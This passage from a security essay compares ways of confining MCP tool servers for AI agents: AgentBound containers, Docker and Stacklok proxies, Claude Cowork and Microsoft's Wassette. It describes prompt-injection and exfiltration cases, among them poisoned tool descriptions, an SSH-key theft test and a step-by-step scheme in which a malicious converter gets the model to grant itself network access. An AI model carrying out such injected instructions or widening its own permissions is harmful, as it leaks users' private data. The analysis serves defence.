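Willison said he would love to believe the result but wanted more independent confirmation. Later that month, Crosley reported in *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary* that the security researcher Johann Rehberger had succeeded against Opus 5 in auto mode in 60–80% of a handful of runs. Rehberger cautioned that his samples were too small to give a general rate. His result doesn't contradict the test's result of zero, because he was looking for one attack that worked, while the test sampled many possible attacks.

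A large number of attacks doesn't guarantee variety. Help Net Security's *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* (2026) describes an experiment in which researchers ran two automated attack tools against the same small model. One tool found 7,132 working attacks and the other 4,282. The researchers retrained a copy of the model on each collection, then tried new attacks on both copies. The copy trained on the larger collection did worse. In the worst case, attacks hijacked 19 of its 40 tasks, compared with 11 for the other copy. The researchers think this is partly because the tools kept rewording the same few tricks. The test was small and used tasks chosen for being easy to attack, but the same pattern appeared in three of the four set-ups.

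These rates are good evidence for choosing one model over another, and that casual attacks on the best models will usually fail. They don't show that an agent can safely hold a confidential contract while a determined attacker tries to get it. Schneier thinks that preventing prompt injection is impossible in the general case, although developers are getting much better at blocking specific attacks. A commenter on his post doubted that anyone had proved this and suggested that models with a different design might keep instructions and data apart, though nobody in the exchange claimed that current models do.

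### Is confining tools beside the point?

The GitHub attack and the currency example suggest that confining tools does not address the main problem, which is that the model can pass data from any tool that holds it to any tool that can send it. The currency tool was as confined as a program can be, and the contract still reached the attacker. AgentBound, which runs local servers in containers, could not stop a poisoned description either. On this view, controlling what the model does with tools would be a better use of effort than sandboxing them. An agent with no sending tool would be safe, but most people want at least one.

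The view is right about leaks that pass through the model, but it doesn't cover leaks that bypass the model, such as the hidden copies that postmark-mcp sent. Confinement stops a malicious converter from uploading a contract whether or not the model is easy to fool. As models get better at resisting injection, attackers have more reason to steal data through a tool's code, where the model never sees the theft.

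The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two also depend on confinement more than their published descriptions make clear. Under both, an agent that must have private data and untrusted inputs should lose its ability to communicate externally. But a local tool server started in the usual way can open network connections. Suppose a designer gives an agent the user's files and a web reader, takes away its email tool, and leaves it an ordinary document converter. The agent appears to have only two of Meta's three properties, but it has all three, because the converter can send its developer every file it receives. Designers must know which tools can communicate externally before they can remove that ability, and they find out through confinement.

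Confinement also makes the remaining leaks easier to detect. If the currency tool has no network connection, its developer has to get the contract out through a call to the email tool. That call contains an address the lawyer never named, and it passes through the client application before anything leaves. Invariant's rule of one repository per session can likewise act only on calls that pass through it.

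Anthropic points out that once a poisoned reply has steered an agent into sending data out, the log shows only a successful, authorised call. A check therefore has to catch the theft before the call goes out. Comparing recipients with the user's own list works well for an email, but there is no such list when the data is hidden in something that looks ordinary, such as the wording of a web search.

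Anthropic drew a similar lesson from its phishing exercise. The instructions came from the user, so neither the model nor a filter had anything unusual to notice. The company concluded that only limits on the agent's environment would have stopped the attack, by blocking the outgoing request or keeping the password file out of reach.

If the lawyer's agent has ten tools and only the email tool can reach the outside world, the client application can concentrate on checking the email tool's calls. If none of the tools is confined, checking calls cannot protect the contract, because a dishonest tool can send it out without making a tool call.

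## AgentBound: running local tool servers in containers

Local tool servers normally start with all of the user's permissions. AgentBound, a research system from the University of St. Gallen in Switzerland, starts each server with none and adds only those the user approves. In *AgentBound*, Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues (2026) tested the system on malicious servers and estimated which permissions popular servers need. Existing servers can run under it without code changes.

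### From the manifest to the firewall

AgentBound copies an idea from Android phones, where each app declares the permissions it needs. Each server comes with a manifest, a short file that describes the server in English and lists its permissions from a fixed vocabulary. The vocabulary covers files, environment variables, running other programs, network connections, devices such as the camera, and the clipboard. For example, the manifest for a tool that fetches web pages lists outgoing network access.

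Suppose the lawyer's client application starts the document converter through AgentBound:

1. The client application reads the converter's manifest, which asks to read and write files but not to use the network.
2. It turns each general permission into a specific one and asks the lawyer to approve it. Reading files becomes read-only access to the folder that holds the contract, and writing files becomes access to a folder for finished PDFs. If the manifest asked for network access, the lawyer would have to approve an exact address.
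3. AgentBound creates a container, an isolated group of processes that shares the machine's operating-system kernel. The container can see the two approved folders and any environment variables the lawyer approved, but none of the lawyer's other files.
4. A script inside the container downloads the converter from npm or PyPI (the main registry for Python packages) and installs it.
5. The script looks up the numerical address of each approved host, adds a firewall rule that permits it, and blocks all other traffic. The converter has no approved hosts, so it loses the network entirely.
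6. The converter starts, and the client application exchanges messages with it as usual.

If the client application requests a permission that the manifest doesn't list, AgentBound stops the launch. The lawyer has to approve anything that changes between runs, such as a new folder. A developer can write fixed details into the manifest, such as the address of the one service that a weather tool uses.

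This is similar to the KeyKOS factory. The user's own software controls what the converter receives, so the lawyer can tell what the converter can reach without reading its code. If the list contains only private folders and no addresses, the converter is close to confined.

The order of steps 4 and 5 leaves a gap. The script sets the firewall rules after it installs the package, because it needs the network to download it. Packages can run code while they install, as the fake Postgres server did. Docker, the software that creates AgentBound's containers, attaches folders and sets environment variables when a container starts. A malicious package could therefore probably read the contract during installation and upload it before the firewall rules exist. Installing the package in a separate container that holds none of the user's data would close this gap.

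The firewall rules are also less precise than the list the lawyer approved. They permit numerical addresses, and many unrelated websites share an address because they use the same hosting company, so approving one site can also allow access to others. Addresses also change, so a server that runs for days could lose contact with a service it is allowed to use.

AgentBound adds little delay. In the researchers' tests on a Mac and a Linux machine, it added about 90 to 430 milliseconds to a server's startup time, not counting the download. Once the server was running, it added less than a millisecond to operations such as reading a file. Starting a fresh copy of a tool for every call, as the factory would, looks practical if the package is already installed.

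### How many servers could start without a network

A client application that started every server without network access would break most of the popular ones. Bühler and colleagues selected the 300 servers with the most GitHub stars (users' bookmarks, a rough measure of popularity) from PulseMCP, a public directory. They were able to download 296 and had OpenAI's GPT-5 models write a manifest for each one from its code and documentation. They then had the manifests written again using Android's list of permissions instead of their own.

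| Permission | Share of servers, AgentBound's list | Share of servers, Android's list |
|---|---|---|
| Outgoing network access | 83.1% | 90.5% |
| Reading environment variables | 79.6% | No match reported |
| Reading files | 74.1% | 50.3% |
| Writing files | 49.3% | 40.8% |

The figure for reading files fell by 24 points when the list changed, so it depends heavily on how the permission is worded. The network figure is steadier and implies that about 50 of the 296 servers need no outgoing connection. The two shares in the first column add up to 157%, so at least 57% of the servers both read files and connect to other machines. A server with both permissions could read a document and upload it.

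Probably fewer than 83.1% of the servers need the open internet, because the permission covers any outgoing connection and so may include servers that only contact a database on the same machine. It also covers connections for optional features. Some of the developers who later reviewed the manifests suggested separating required permissions from optional ones.

An earlier survey found less network use. In *We Urgently Need Privilege Management in MCP*, Li, Li and colleagues (2025) searched the source code of 2,562 servers from the directory MCP Market for functions that use sensitive resources. They found network functions in 1,438 (56%), system functions such as those that start other programs in 1,237 (48%), and file functions in 613 (24%). Their search skipped third-party libraries, so it could miss a server that contacts a service through that service's own library. The true share of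 servers that use the network is likely to be higher than 56%.

The two surveys also looked at different kinds of server. Every server in AgentBound's sample had at least 59 stars, while 72% of those in the earlier survey had ten or fewer. The earlier survey's table of sensitive calls by star count seems to count servers instead of calls, because the counts for all the groups add up to exactly 2,562, the number of servers, and the network counts add up to 1,438. Li and colleagues concluded from the table that less popular servers do riskier things, since it lists 1,837 for servers with up to ten stars and far fewer for every other group. If the table counts servers, that difference only shows that most servers have few stars.

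Read that way, the data point in the opposite direction. File functions appear in 20% of servers with up to ten stars and in 67% of the 57 servers with more than 1,000. Network use rises less steadily, appearing in 59% of servers with up to ten stars, 47% of those with 11 to 1,000, and 74% of those with more. Popular servers seem to use more of the machine, perhaps because they have more features. This difference would explain part of the gap between the surveys.

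Together, the surveys suggest that between 17% and 44% of servers could work normally without a network connection. A client application could still block network access by default, as AgentBound does, and let users approve addresses for the other servers. For a weather tool, that means approving one address. A tool that fetches any page the user asks for can't work with a short list of approved addresses.

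### Stealing a login key

To check whether the limits work, Bühler and colleagues wrote a server that tries to steal the user's private SSH key, a file that lets anyone who has it log in to other machines as the user. They ran the server under three sets of limits.

| Limits on the server | Could it read the key? | Could it send the key out? |
|---|---|---|
| None | Yes | Yes |
| No network | Yes | No |
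| No access to the key file | No | It had nothing to send |

Blocking the network stopped the direct theft, but the server still had the key and could have returned it in a reply. The model might then have passed the key to a tool with network access, as happened with private data in the GitHub attack. Errico, Ngiam and Sojan (2025) warn in *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* that network isolation gives limited protection when an agent uses several servers. All three work for companies that sell security or MCP products, but their warning follows directly from how agents work.

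Servers without malicious code can also leak files through their replies. *My Credentials, Please* (2026) examines local servers whose tools look harmless. The attacker plants text that influences an argument the agent gives to a tool, such as a file path. Because the server runs with the user's permissions, it can open a file unrelated to the tool's purpose and return the contents. The theft needs no network connection from the server. Making the file inaccessible to the server prevents it.

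Network limits are not enough without file limits. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* points out that a compromised agent with no file limits could easily escape its sandbox and regain network access. For example, it might change a settings file that a program outside the sandbox trusts.

### Which attacks got through

The researchers also ran fourteen servers from public collections of attacks. Four were ordinary tools with known weaknesses or attacks built in, and the other ten came from Damn Vulnerable MCP Server, a set of deliberately unsafe servers for security testing. AgentBound stopped eight of the attacks completely and one partly, and the other five got through.

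| Tool | Attack | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Google Maps | The code contacts the attacker's machine instead of Google's | Stopped |
| Weather | The code contacts a different machine, as in the Google Maps tool | Stopped |
| Time zones | The description tells the model to redirect cryptocurrency transfers | Got through |
| WeChat | Malicious input changes a database query (SQL injection) | Got through |

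The Google Maps tool shows why limiting what a program can do can work better than looking for suspicious code. Its developer had stored the attacker's address as lists of character codes, so someone who skimmed the source would not have seen it. AgentBound didn't need to recognise the address, because its firewall blocked every address except Google's.

The time-zone tool worked like the currency tool in the previous section. Its description instructed the model to send any payment made with a separate wallet tool through a "privacy proxy", which was the attacker's account. The time-zone tool never tried to leave its container, and the wallet tool made the kind of payment it was built to make. The WeChat attack used a database that the server needed for its normal work.

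AgentBound completely stopped six of the ten test servers. Those six included servers with poisoned tool descriptions, a description that changed after a few uses, or tools that allowed access to files or system commands. AgentBound did not stop three others. Two of these planted text that affected only the model, and the third had a flaw that didn't involve the machine's files or connections. The last server combined several attacks, and AgentBound blocked those that needed forbidden files or addresses.

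AgentBound can still block an attack from a poisoned tool description if the model has to use a restricted tool to carry it out. In the paper's example, an agent writes documentation using a file tool and a web-fetching tool. The attacker's text tells the model to empty every file it reads and send the contents to a malicious website. Both instructions fail because the file tool can only read the source code and the web tool can only contact the documentation site. The second instruction would work if the attacker could collect data from a page on the approved site.

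AgentBound would not have stopped postmark-mcp, because Postmark would have had to be on the approved list.

Nine out of fourteen is a poor guide to how often AgentBound would stop real attacks, because the number depends on which attacks the collections contained. The researchers also chose the limits themselves, writing the manifests for the ten test servers by hand and using manifests made from the original, harmless versions for the other four. A malicious developer would write a manifest to suit the attack. The Google Maps attacker could list a second address, describe it as a source of map images, and wait for users to approve it.

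### How accurate are the manifests?

Most servers don't have a manifest yet, so Bühler and colleagues propose generating a draft automatically and letting the developer correct it. They report that the generated manifests are 80.9% accurate, based on a small number of replies.

The researchers sent manifests to the developers of 96 servers and asked whether the permissions were correct and complete. Of these developers, 71 (about 74%) did not reply, 17 accepted the manifest, 4 rejected it, and 4 were still discussing it. The reported accuracy appears to be the 17 acceptances divided by the 21 clear answers, or 81%. With so few answers, the 95% confidence interval runs from about 60% to 92%, and that assumes the developers who replied were typical. The manifests may have been equally good for the other servers, but developers confirmed only 17.7% of the 96.

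In one correction, a developer asked to limit access to the environment variables that the server uses, which AgentBound already asks for at launch. Another developer pointed out that a server did not need to read files, because it only contacted online services.

In a second check, which doesn't depend on who replied, two of the researchers wrote manifests by hand for 48 servers, 24 each, and compared them with the generated ones. Of 816 decisions (17 permissions for each server), 787 matched, or 96.4%. That rate is less impressive than it sounds because most servers need few permissions. In the larger survey, servers averaged about 2.9 of the four most common permissions, so a blank manifest would get roughly 80% of the decisions right.

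The generated manifest was identical to the handwritten one for 28 of the 48 servers (58%) and differed by a single permission for another 14. Of the 29 mismatched permissions, 23 were missing from the generated manifest. Omissions are the safer kind of error, because they can break a feature but don't give a server authority it doesn't need.

Even an accurate general manifest isn't enough to distinguish an honest server from a dishonest one. The honest and dishonest versions of the Google Maps tool would have the same manifest because both use the network. They differ only in the addresses they contact, which the user has to approve.

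### Relying on the user's consent

The 93% approval rate in Claude Code suggests that dialogs are a weak place to put that decision. Anthropic found that experienced users approved actions automatically about twice as often as new users, but also interrupted the agent more often. Many seem to have switched from checking each step to watching for signs of trouble. This doesn't work well against a tool that leaks data, because the leak may take less than a second and show no sign.

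AgentBound prompts the user less often than Claude Code. It requests approval for access to a folder or an address when a server starts, rather than for each action. People may read a few prompts more carefully than a long stream of them, but the AgentBound experiments can't show whether they do, because a single tester gave consent in all the security tests.

The lawyer could also approve permissions one at a time that each seem reasonable but are dangerous in combination. A converter needs to read the folder of contracts. It might also ask to contact a font service, which sounds harmless to a non-expert. With both permissions, the converter could upload every contract in the folder to whoever runs the font service. A client application could show both permissions in one dialog and explain that the converter would be able to send the contracts to the font service.

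The scope of an approval also matters. Infosecurity Magazine reports a test in which the company Ox Security connected a malicious MCP server to Claude Code running Haiku 3.5, an old, small model. The server first requested a harmless file, and the user chose "always allow". It then requested a sensitive file, such as `.env`, where developers often keep passwords, and got it without another prompt. According to Ox, Anthropic replied that this is the documented behaviour of "always allow", and that the model's detection of malicious content is a best effort and not a security boundary.

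A newer model might have refused the second request, but the permission would still have allowed it. AgentBound's narrower approvals cover a particular folder, so they would have protected a `.env` file stored elsewhere. But developers usually keep that file in the project's main folder, so a user who approved the whole project would have exposed it.

Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received three reports of flaws that let an attacker's code run in Claude Code before the user had agreed to anything. In one case, a downloaded project's settings file contained a command that ran automatically, because Claude Code read the file at startup, before asking whether the user trusted the folder. Anthropic fixed the flaws by making Claude Code wait for the user's answer before reading the project's settings.

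Fixed limits reduce the need for permission prompts. When Anthropic added a sandbox to Claude Code that confined writing to the project's folder and blocked the network by default, permission prompts fell by 84%. Anthropic put Claude Cowork, its agent for office work, in a virtual machine because it decided that it couldn't expect users to judge technical commands.

### What a virtual machine adds

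Containers share a kernel, the core of the operating system, which opens files and network connections for every program and enforces each container's limits. A malicious server that exploited a flaw in the kernel could therefore escape its container. Bühler and colleagues acknowledge that AgentBound depends on the security of the Linux kernel and Docker, and suggest adding more layers of protection.

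A virtual machine has its own kernel. A program called the hypervisor divides the hardware between virtual machines and keeps them apart, so a server that takes over the kernel inside one still has to break through the hypervisor to reach the rest of the computer. A microVM is a small virtual machine that isolates a single workload and is designed to start quickly. Giving each tool server its own microVM would limit the damage from a kernel flaw to that server.

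Docker Desktop, the version of Docker for Macs and Windows PCs, runs its containers inside a shared Linux virtual machine. On the Mac in the AgentBound tests, a server that escaped its container through a kernel flaw would have reached that virtual machine first. It could then have interfered with other containers and any folders they shared with the Mac.

One middle option is to run code in containers that use gVisor, as Claude's website does. gVisor handles most of a program's requests in a separate layer before they reach the machine's kernel. Anthropic's *Sandbox environments* compares options for Claude Code, from a light sandbox around individual commands to a separate virtual machine.

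Many escapes don't need a kernel flaw because the container already has too much access. *MCP-38* describes two examples. A server that can write to a folder on the user's machine can put a malicious script there and get it to run outside the container. A server with access to Docker's control socket, which programs use to send Docker commands, can start a new container with access to the entire disk. A virtual machine would not make the shared folder safe, since the user might still run the script.

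Neither a container nor a virtual machine can stop a server from sending data to an address the user has approved. Anthropic says the hypervisor and other established isolation software in its products have been dependable. Its own network address filter failed and let files leave Cowork through an approved address.

Virtual machines take longer to start than containers, and they hide activity from the security software that companies run on employees' computers. Anthropic's corporate customers asked why their tools couldn't monitor activity inside Cowork. The company offers event logs that administrators can collect afterwards, but concedes that these are not the same as live monitoring.

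For most third-party tools, the network and file limits probably matter more than the choice between a container and a microVM. The postmark-mcp attack took one line of code and no sandbox escape. Stronger isolation will matter more if limits become common and attackers have to look for ways around them.

### How Docker and Stacklok run tool servers

Docker, the company behind the container software, encourages developers to run MCP servers in containers. Docker's *Securing Model Context Protocol* (2025) presents a catalogue of servers packaged as ready-to-run containers, and a gateway that carries all messages between them and the client application. Because the packages are already built, the user's machine doesn't have to run installation scripts alongside the user's data. The gateway can require fresh approval when a tool's description changes, and each secret goes only to the containers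 permitted to use it.

The basic command in Docker's article creates a new container and deletes it when the server exits, so each run starts clean. But the command doesn't restrict network access, and Docker containers can normally open outgoing connections. A converter started this way couldn't see the lawyer's other files but could still upload the contract.

Docker suggests that a server's annotations could help set the limits. For example, a tool annotated as read-only could run with read-only access to files. This is safer than trusting the annotation alone, because the container would enforce it. But a malicious developer can leave the annotation out, so this helps only if the limits are already strict for servers without annotations.

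*Who are your MCP servers talking to?*, by the software company Stacklok, explains that the company's ToolHive product puts each server in a container and sends its outgoing traffic through a proxy, a program that decides which connections to allow. In Stacklok's demonstration, a web-fetching server was allowed to contact only `stacklok.com`. When GitHub's Copilot assistant asked it to fetch a page from `anthropic.com`, the proxy blocked the connection and logged the attempt.

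The proxy checks host names, so it can distinguish unrelated sites that share an IP address. It can also block the network completely, which is the right setting for a document converter. In Stacklok's examples, though, these limits apply only if the user turns on network isolation with an option in the launch command.

If users don't know which connections a server needs, Stacklok advises them to start it with no network access and check the log for refused connections. This is a quick way to build a list of allowed addresses for a harmless server, but a malicious server's log would also contain the attacker's address, and a user who wanted the tool to work might approve it. ToolHive's default list for GitHub's own server permits GitHub's domains, so it would not have stopped the GitHub attack.

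### Where Claude Cowork runs local plugin servers

Claude Cowork restricts third-party local tool servers less than it restricts code that Claude writes. According to Anthropic's *Claude Cowork desktop architecture overview*, shell commands and Claude's code run in a Linux virtual machine, while the local MCP servers that come with plugins run directly on the user's computer.

Cowork's permission system controls what happens outside the virtual machine. It can block a tool call or keep Claude out of a folder. But a local server is a separate program, and the operating system normally lets it open files and connections without Cowork's approval. Anthropic compares these servers to any other software a user chooses to install.

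Local servers used to run inside the virtual machine. Anthropic says it moved them out because they were harder to audit there, updates to the virtual machine broke software they depended on, and some needed to reach other programs on the computer, such as databases. It wanted Cowork to treat local servers as its Claude Desktop application already did.

These are good reasons not to put every server in one shared virtual machine, but each server could still be confined separately. A server's container can include the software that server needs, so an update elsewhere won't break it. The user can also approve a connection to one local database without giving the server access to the rest of the computer. AgentBound's approach could do both, although someone would have to maintain the containers and help users whose tools stopped working.

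The audit argument is stronger. Security software can watch a program that runs directly on the machine, and administrators can read its code and pin its version. Automated scanners are a poor substitute for that work. *Rethinking MCP Security*, a study of 64,611 servers, found that existing scanners flagged 96.89% of them as risky, but fewer than half of the alerts checked by hand were correct. An administrator who relied on such a scanner would have to reject nearly every server or ignore the warnings.

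Companies can turn off local servers in Cowork. One setting disables MCP servers from plugins and local configuration files, and another disables servers packaged as desktop extensions. Both apply to whole devices, so they can protect a law firm that is willing to do without such tools, but they can't confine one converter while leaving the others alone.

Local MCP servers still run on the user's computer, even though Cowork's own work has moved to the cloud. According to Anthropic's *Getting started with Cowork*, tasks now run in an isolated environment on the company's servers. But local MCP servers, including those in plugins, still need the desktop application, according to Anthropic's *What to expect with Claude Cowork in the cloud*. If the lawyer asks Cowork to convert the contract, a script that Claude writes for the job runs in isolation, but a stranger's converter installed as a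 local plugin runs on the lawyer's own computer and can read the other contracts stored there.

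## Wassette: running tools as WebAssembly components

Wassette, an open-source project that Microsoft started in 2025, runs tools as WebAssembly components, which cannot open a file until someone grants them access. WebAssembly is a format for compiled code that the major web browsers adopted in 2017. Browsers run untrusted code on almost every page, so the format had to prevent that code from accessing the visitor's disk. AgentBound, by contrast, starts with a program that could open any of the user's files and builds a container around it.

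### Code that starts with nothing

The WebAssembly System Interface (WASI) is a standard set of functions that give WebAssembly code access to files, networks and clocks. According to WASI's *Security*, code that runs under WASI starts with no access to the outside world. An ordinary process, by contrast, starts with its user's permissions, which a sandbox has to take away.

A WebAssembly component can do arithmetic, use its own memory and call functions. To reach anything outside itself, it must import a function, and the runtime (the program that executes the component) has to supply that function before the component can start. Files, network connections, clocks, random numbers and environment variables have separate imports, so a runtime can supply a clock without supplying network access.

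If the dishonest document converter is a component, its extra lines need a network function from the runtime to upload the contract. If the runtime doesn't supply one, the converter won't start. The runtime can also supply a network function that blocks every address, so the converter starts and makes the PDF but the upload fails. Wassette supplies blocking functions like this, which lets a user add permissions after the tool has loaded.

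Wassette components have no network access until the user grants it, so if the user forgets, a tool that needs the network fails and the user will soon notice. Docker containers have network access by default, so a tool still works if the user forgets to switch it off, but it can leak data.

The imports are also part of the compiled file, so anyone can list them without running the component or seeing its source code. This is close to the check that the KeyKOS factory made. If a converter's file has no import for sockets or web requests, the converter cannot open a connection, whatever its developer wrote. Finding a network import is much weaker evidence, because the toolkits that compile components often add imports that the tool never uses. The check doesn't work for files in the older WASI Preview 1 format, where access depends on what the runtime grants at launch, but Wassette accepts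 only components.

### From a registry to an MCP tool

Wassette is a local MCP server. The user connects the client application to it once, and it runs any number of tools behind that connection, each in its own sandbox. It runs them with Wasmtime, a runtime maintained by the Bytecode Alliance. In its launch post, Microsoft said the goal was for agents to find and load tools they lack, with the user's consent at key moments.

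Microsoft's *What is Wassette?* sets out the loading sequence. For a weather tool it goes like this:

1. The agent calls Wassette's `load-component` tool with the component's address. In Microsoft's demonstration, GitHub's Copilot assistant asks the user to confirm the address first.
2. Wassette downloads the file, usually from a registry of the kind that stores container images. It also accepts local files and ordinary web addresses.
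3. Wasmtime compiles the file, and Wassette reads the component's interface. The interface is a typed list of functions, such as `get-weather`, which takes a location as text and returns either text or an error.
4. Wassette turns each function into an MCP tool with a name and a schema of its arguments. The example in Microsoft's *Core Concepts* becomes `example_weather_weather_api_get_weather`.
5. Wassette applies a default policy, which grants no files, network addresses or environment variables.
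6. When the agent calls the tool, Wassette creates an instance of the component under the current policy, runs the function and returns the result.

The sequence doesn't include a signature check, although Microsoft lists signature verification among Wassette's architectural goals and says in its launch post that developers can sign components with Notation and Cosign. Users can do the check themselves. wasmCloud (2025), another project that runs WebAssembly components, published instructions for signing a component with Cosign, storing the signature beside it in the registry and verifying it before the component runs. The signature ties the file to an identity, such as the publisher's account, without requiring the publisher to keep a long-lived secret key.

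A signature would have helped against postmark-mcp only if users had insisted on Postmark's own, because the developer who copied Postmark's code could have validly signed the copy with his own account. Microsoft's *MCP Threat Model* (2025) acknowledges the related problem that someone who takes over a developer's account can publish signed malicious components.

Updates are less risky with Wassette than with tools that download their newest version at every start. Wassette keeps the loaded file on disk and doesn't change it while it is in use, so a new version should arrive only when someone loads the component again. But the addresses in Microsoft's examples end in `:latest`, a label that the publisher can move to a different file. Naming the file by its cryptographic hash would avoid this. Wassette also stores each policy under the component's ID, so a replacement with the same ID may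 inherit the permissions that the user gave the old version.

The developer still writes the description that the model reads. Comments in the interface can become the tool's description, so a malicious currency tool could still include its false legal requirement when it runs in Wassette. Microsoft's threat model has a section on tool poisoning, but it uses the term to mean corrupted inputs and settings, and the defences it lists don't address instructions hidden in a description.

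### A weather tool with one address

Suppose a user wants the weather tool to contact one forecasting service and nothing else. The whole policy is:

```yaml
version: "1.0"
description: "Weather tool, one address"
permissions:
  network:
    allow:
      - host: "api.weather.com"
```

Wassette saves the policy in a file beside the component. The policy has no storage or environment entries, so the tool can't access files or environment variables.

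| What the tool tries to do | Result |
|---|---|
| Request the forecast for New York from `api.weather.com` | The request goes through |
| Upload text to the developer's own server | Wassette refuses, and the tool gets an error |
| Open the lawyer's contract | Wassette refuses, and the tool gets an error |
| Read a password from the environment | The tool finds no such variable |
| Add extra text to its request to `api.weather.com` | The request goes through |

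The last row describes the gap that an address allowlist would have left open for postmark-mcp. For the weather tool, the gap matters mainly if the developer can see the requests, which could happen if the tool used the developer's own account with the forecasting service and the service showed customers their past queries.

If the service requires a key, the user can also grant the tool access to the environment variable that holds it. The tool could then read that key and no others, and send it only to the forecasting service.

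Wassette checks host names, as Stacklok's proxy does, which is more precise than AgentBound's firewall. Microsoft claims that this also stops attackers who tamper with DNS to redirect a request, but it can't, because a redirected request still has the right host name. If the connection is encrypted, the certificate check would normally catch the redirection.

Wassette could also be extended to check the contents of requests, which its policy format has no rules for. When a component uses the standard web-request function, the runtime receives the address, headers and body before they are encrypted. The runtime could then run the recipient check that would have stopped postmark-mcp, without having to get a server to accept another program's certificate. It would have to refuse any component that made its own encrypted connection through a lower-level socket.

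Users can also write policies that are much too broad. The threat model describes network permissions as naming individual hosts, not wildcards, but Microsoft's *Managing Permissions* allows entries such as `*.example.com`. It also lists commonly used domains, including `*.s3.amazonaws.com` and `*.blob.core.windows.net`, where Amazon and Microsoft host their customers' files. Anyone can rent storage there, so a user who copied one of these entries to get a tool working would give the tool's developer a place to upload documents. Microsoft does tell users to grant only the domains that a component needs.

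When Wassette refuses a request, it returns an error to the component without alerting the user. Microsoft advises users to turn on detailed logging if they want to see the attempt. A weather tool that tried to upload a contract therefore looks to the user like one that lacks a permission it needs.

### Comparing Wassette with a factory

According to Microsoft's threat model, Wassette creates a fresh instance with its own memory for every call, whereas a factory makes a fresh copy for each customer. The call sequence in the manual is consistent with this. Separate instances prevent one customer's contract from appearing in a reply to another, unless the converter has saved the contract to a file.

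Some of Microsoft's examples don't fit this design. The manual's Rust guide includes a "stateful" component that keeps a list in memory and returns it in a later call, and Wassette's *Changelog* describes an example server that stores a graph of facts with "in-memory persistence". If every call gets a new instance, both would lose their data between calls. The threat model and the call sequence are probably more reliable, since they describe the mechanism directly, but anyone who depends on each call getting a new instance should test it by storing a word in one call and asking for it in the next.

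A component with access to storage can keep data between calls. Microsoft's sample policy for untrusted components lets them read and write a folder in `/tmp`, the machine's shared directory for temporary files. A converter with that grant could save one contract and read it again during a later call. Depending on the folder's settings, other programs on the machine might also be able to read the contract. It would be safer to give each call its own scratch folder and delete it afterwards, as in the factory example.

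A component also gets more access than its policy lists. Microsoft's demonstration loads a clock tool that reports the time without asking for any permission, and the policy format has no entry for clocks, so Wassette evidently gives every component a clock. A clock makes it easier to leak data through timing. Wassette's sandbox blocks several covert channels by keeping components away from shared memory and other processes, but a component can still signal through processor load, as the factory's converter could. Microsoft's claim that the sandbox prevents components from using covert channels is therefore too strong. Signalling through processor load is slow, though, and few attackers would bother with it while easier methods exist.

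#### What a caller can verify

Wassette offers a weaker version of the factory's check. The command `wassette policy get` prints a component's current permissions. The agent has a `get-policy` tool, but the sample reply in Microsoft's *Built-in Tools* gives the policy's ID, source and location on disk, not its permissions.

Even a complete list can go out of date, because a Wassette policy can change between the check and the call. If someone makes the change through Wassette's own commands, it takes effect without a restart. By contrast, the result of checking a sealed factory held for every later copy.

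The component's imports would give a firmer answer. If the lawyer's converter has no network import, it cannot upload anything, even if someone later grants it access to an address, because the compiled file contains no call that could use the permission. This holds until someone replaces the file. The `wassette inspect` command shows only a tool's inputs and outputs, but the developer utility wasm-tools can also print the component's imports. A client application could check every converter's imports before loading it, reject any with a network import, and then monitor only the storage grants.

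### The model can widen the policy

Wassette's built-in tools include `grant-network-permission`, `grant-storage-permission` and `grant-environment-variable-permission`. These are ordinary MCP tools, so the model can call them. Microsoft recommends that users normally manage permissions by asking the agent in plain language to make these calls.

Microsoft treats the agent as untrusted in its threat model and says that Wassette enforces permissions where the agent cannot interfere. A manipulated model cannot make a component exceed its policy, but it can request a policy change through Wassette. In Microsoft's example, a document contains hidden instructions to read a password file and post it to `attacker.com`. Microsoft says the attack fails because neither tool has the permission it needs. The attack could succeed if the hidden instructions first had the model grant both permissions.

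A dishonest converter could do the same without any planted document:

1. The lawyer loads the converter with access to one folder and no network.
2. On the first call, the converter returns an error saying that it needs `fonts.example` to load the contract's typefaces.
3. The model, trying to finish the job, calls `grant-network-permission` for that host.
4. The client application asks the lawyer to confirm, unless the lawyer has already chosen to allow the tool every time.
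5. On the second call, the converter makes a good PDF and uploads the contract. (It needs a network import for this, which a check of the file would have revealed.)

Step 2 looks like normal use. In Microsoft's demonstration, Copilot asks the user to grant a web-fetching tool access to a site to summarise a page. The launch post warns that agents sometimes need prompting at this point and suggests "please fix the permission errors." If a malicious tool is loaded, a user who types that is asking the model to remove the protection.

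The client application's confirmation question is the only barrier left. It is short and names the host, but the lawyer has no way of knowing who runs `fonts.example`.

Users can close most of this gap by starting Wassette with `--disable-builtin-tools`, an option that Microsoft added in November 2025. It removes all the management tools, leaving the model only the tools that the user has already loaded. The user sets permissions beforehand on the command line. The agent loses the feature that Microsoft promotes most, the ability to fetch new tools for itself.

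The option isn't enough if the agent can also run shell commands, as most coding agents can, because the agent could run `wassette permission grant` itself or edit the policy file directly. The same November release added written instructions for AI agents to use the grant tools instead of editing policy files, presumably because some agents had been editing the files. *Permission System Design* (Mossaka, 2025) listed signatures and checksums for policies only as future work. Any other program with the user's permissions, including an unconfined tool server, could also edit the files, although Wassette may need a restart before it applies such an edit. It is probably safest to run Wassette under a separate account or in a container, with the policies stored where neither the agent nor its other tools can write.

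### Rewriting tools and trusting the runtime

Unlike AgentBound, Wassette can't run existing servers. According to Microsoft's *Frequently Asked Questions (FAQ)*, developers must rewrite them as functions that compile to components. A rewritten weather tool can be shorter than the original because Wassette handles the MCP messages. Microsoft calls this rewriting the biggest barrier to adoption. It has published a guide for converting JavaScript servers and says it is exploring AI tools to help with the work.

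The difficulty depends on the language:

| Language | How developers build components | Main limits |
|---|---|---|
| Rust | The standard Rust compiler | Few, since Rust has the most extensive tooling |
| JavaScript and TypeScript | A toolkit named jco | Packages that rely on Node.js's own file and network functions may fail |
| Python | A toolkit named componentize-py | Packages that include compiled code may fail, so Microsoft advises the standard library and pure Python |
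| Go | TinyGo, an alternative compiler | No C code, limited concurrency and missing parts of the standard library |

A component also can't start other programs. For example, document converters are easy to confine in principle, but many pass the work to a large program such as LibreOffice. A developer would have to compile that program to WebAssembly or find a simpler library that does the job less well.

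Wassette supports only MCP tools, not prompts or resources, the other things that an MCP server can offer. A server that depends on prompts or resources would lose them even after a rewrite.

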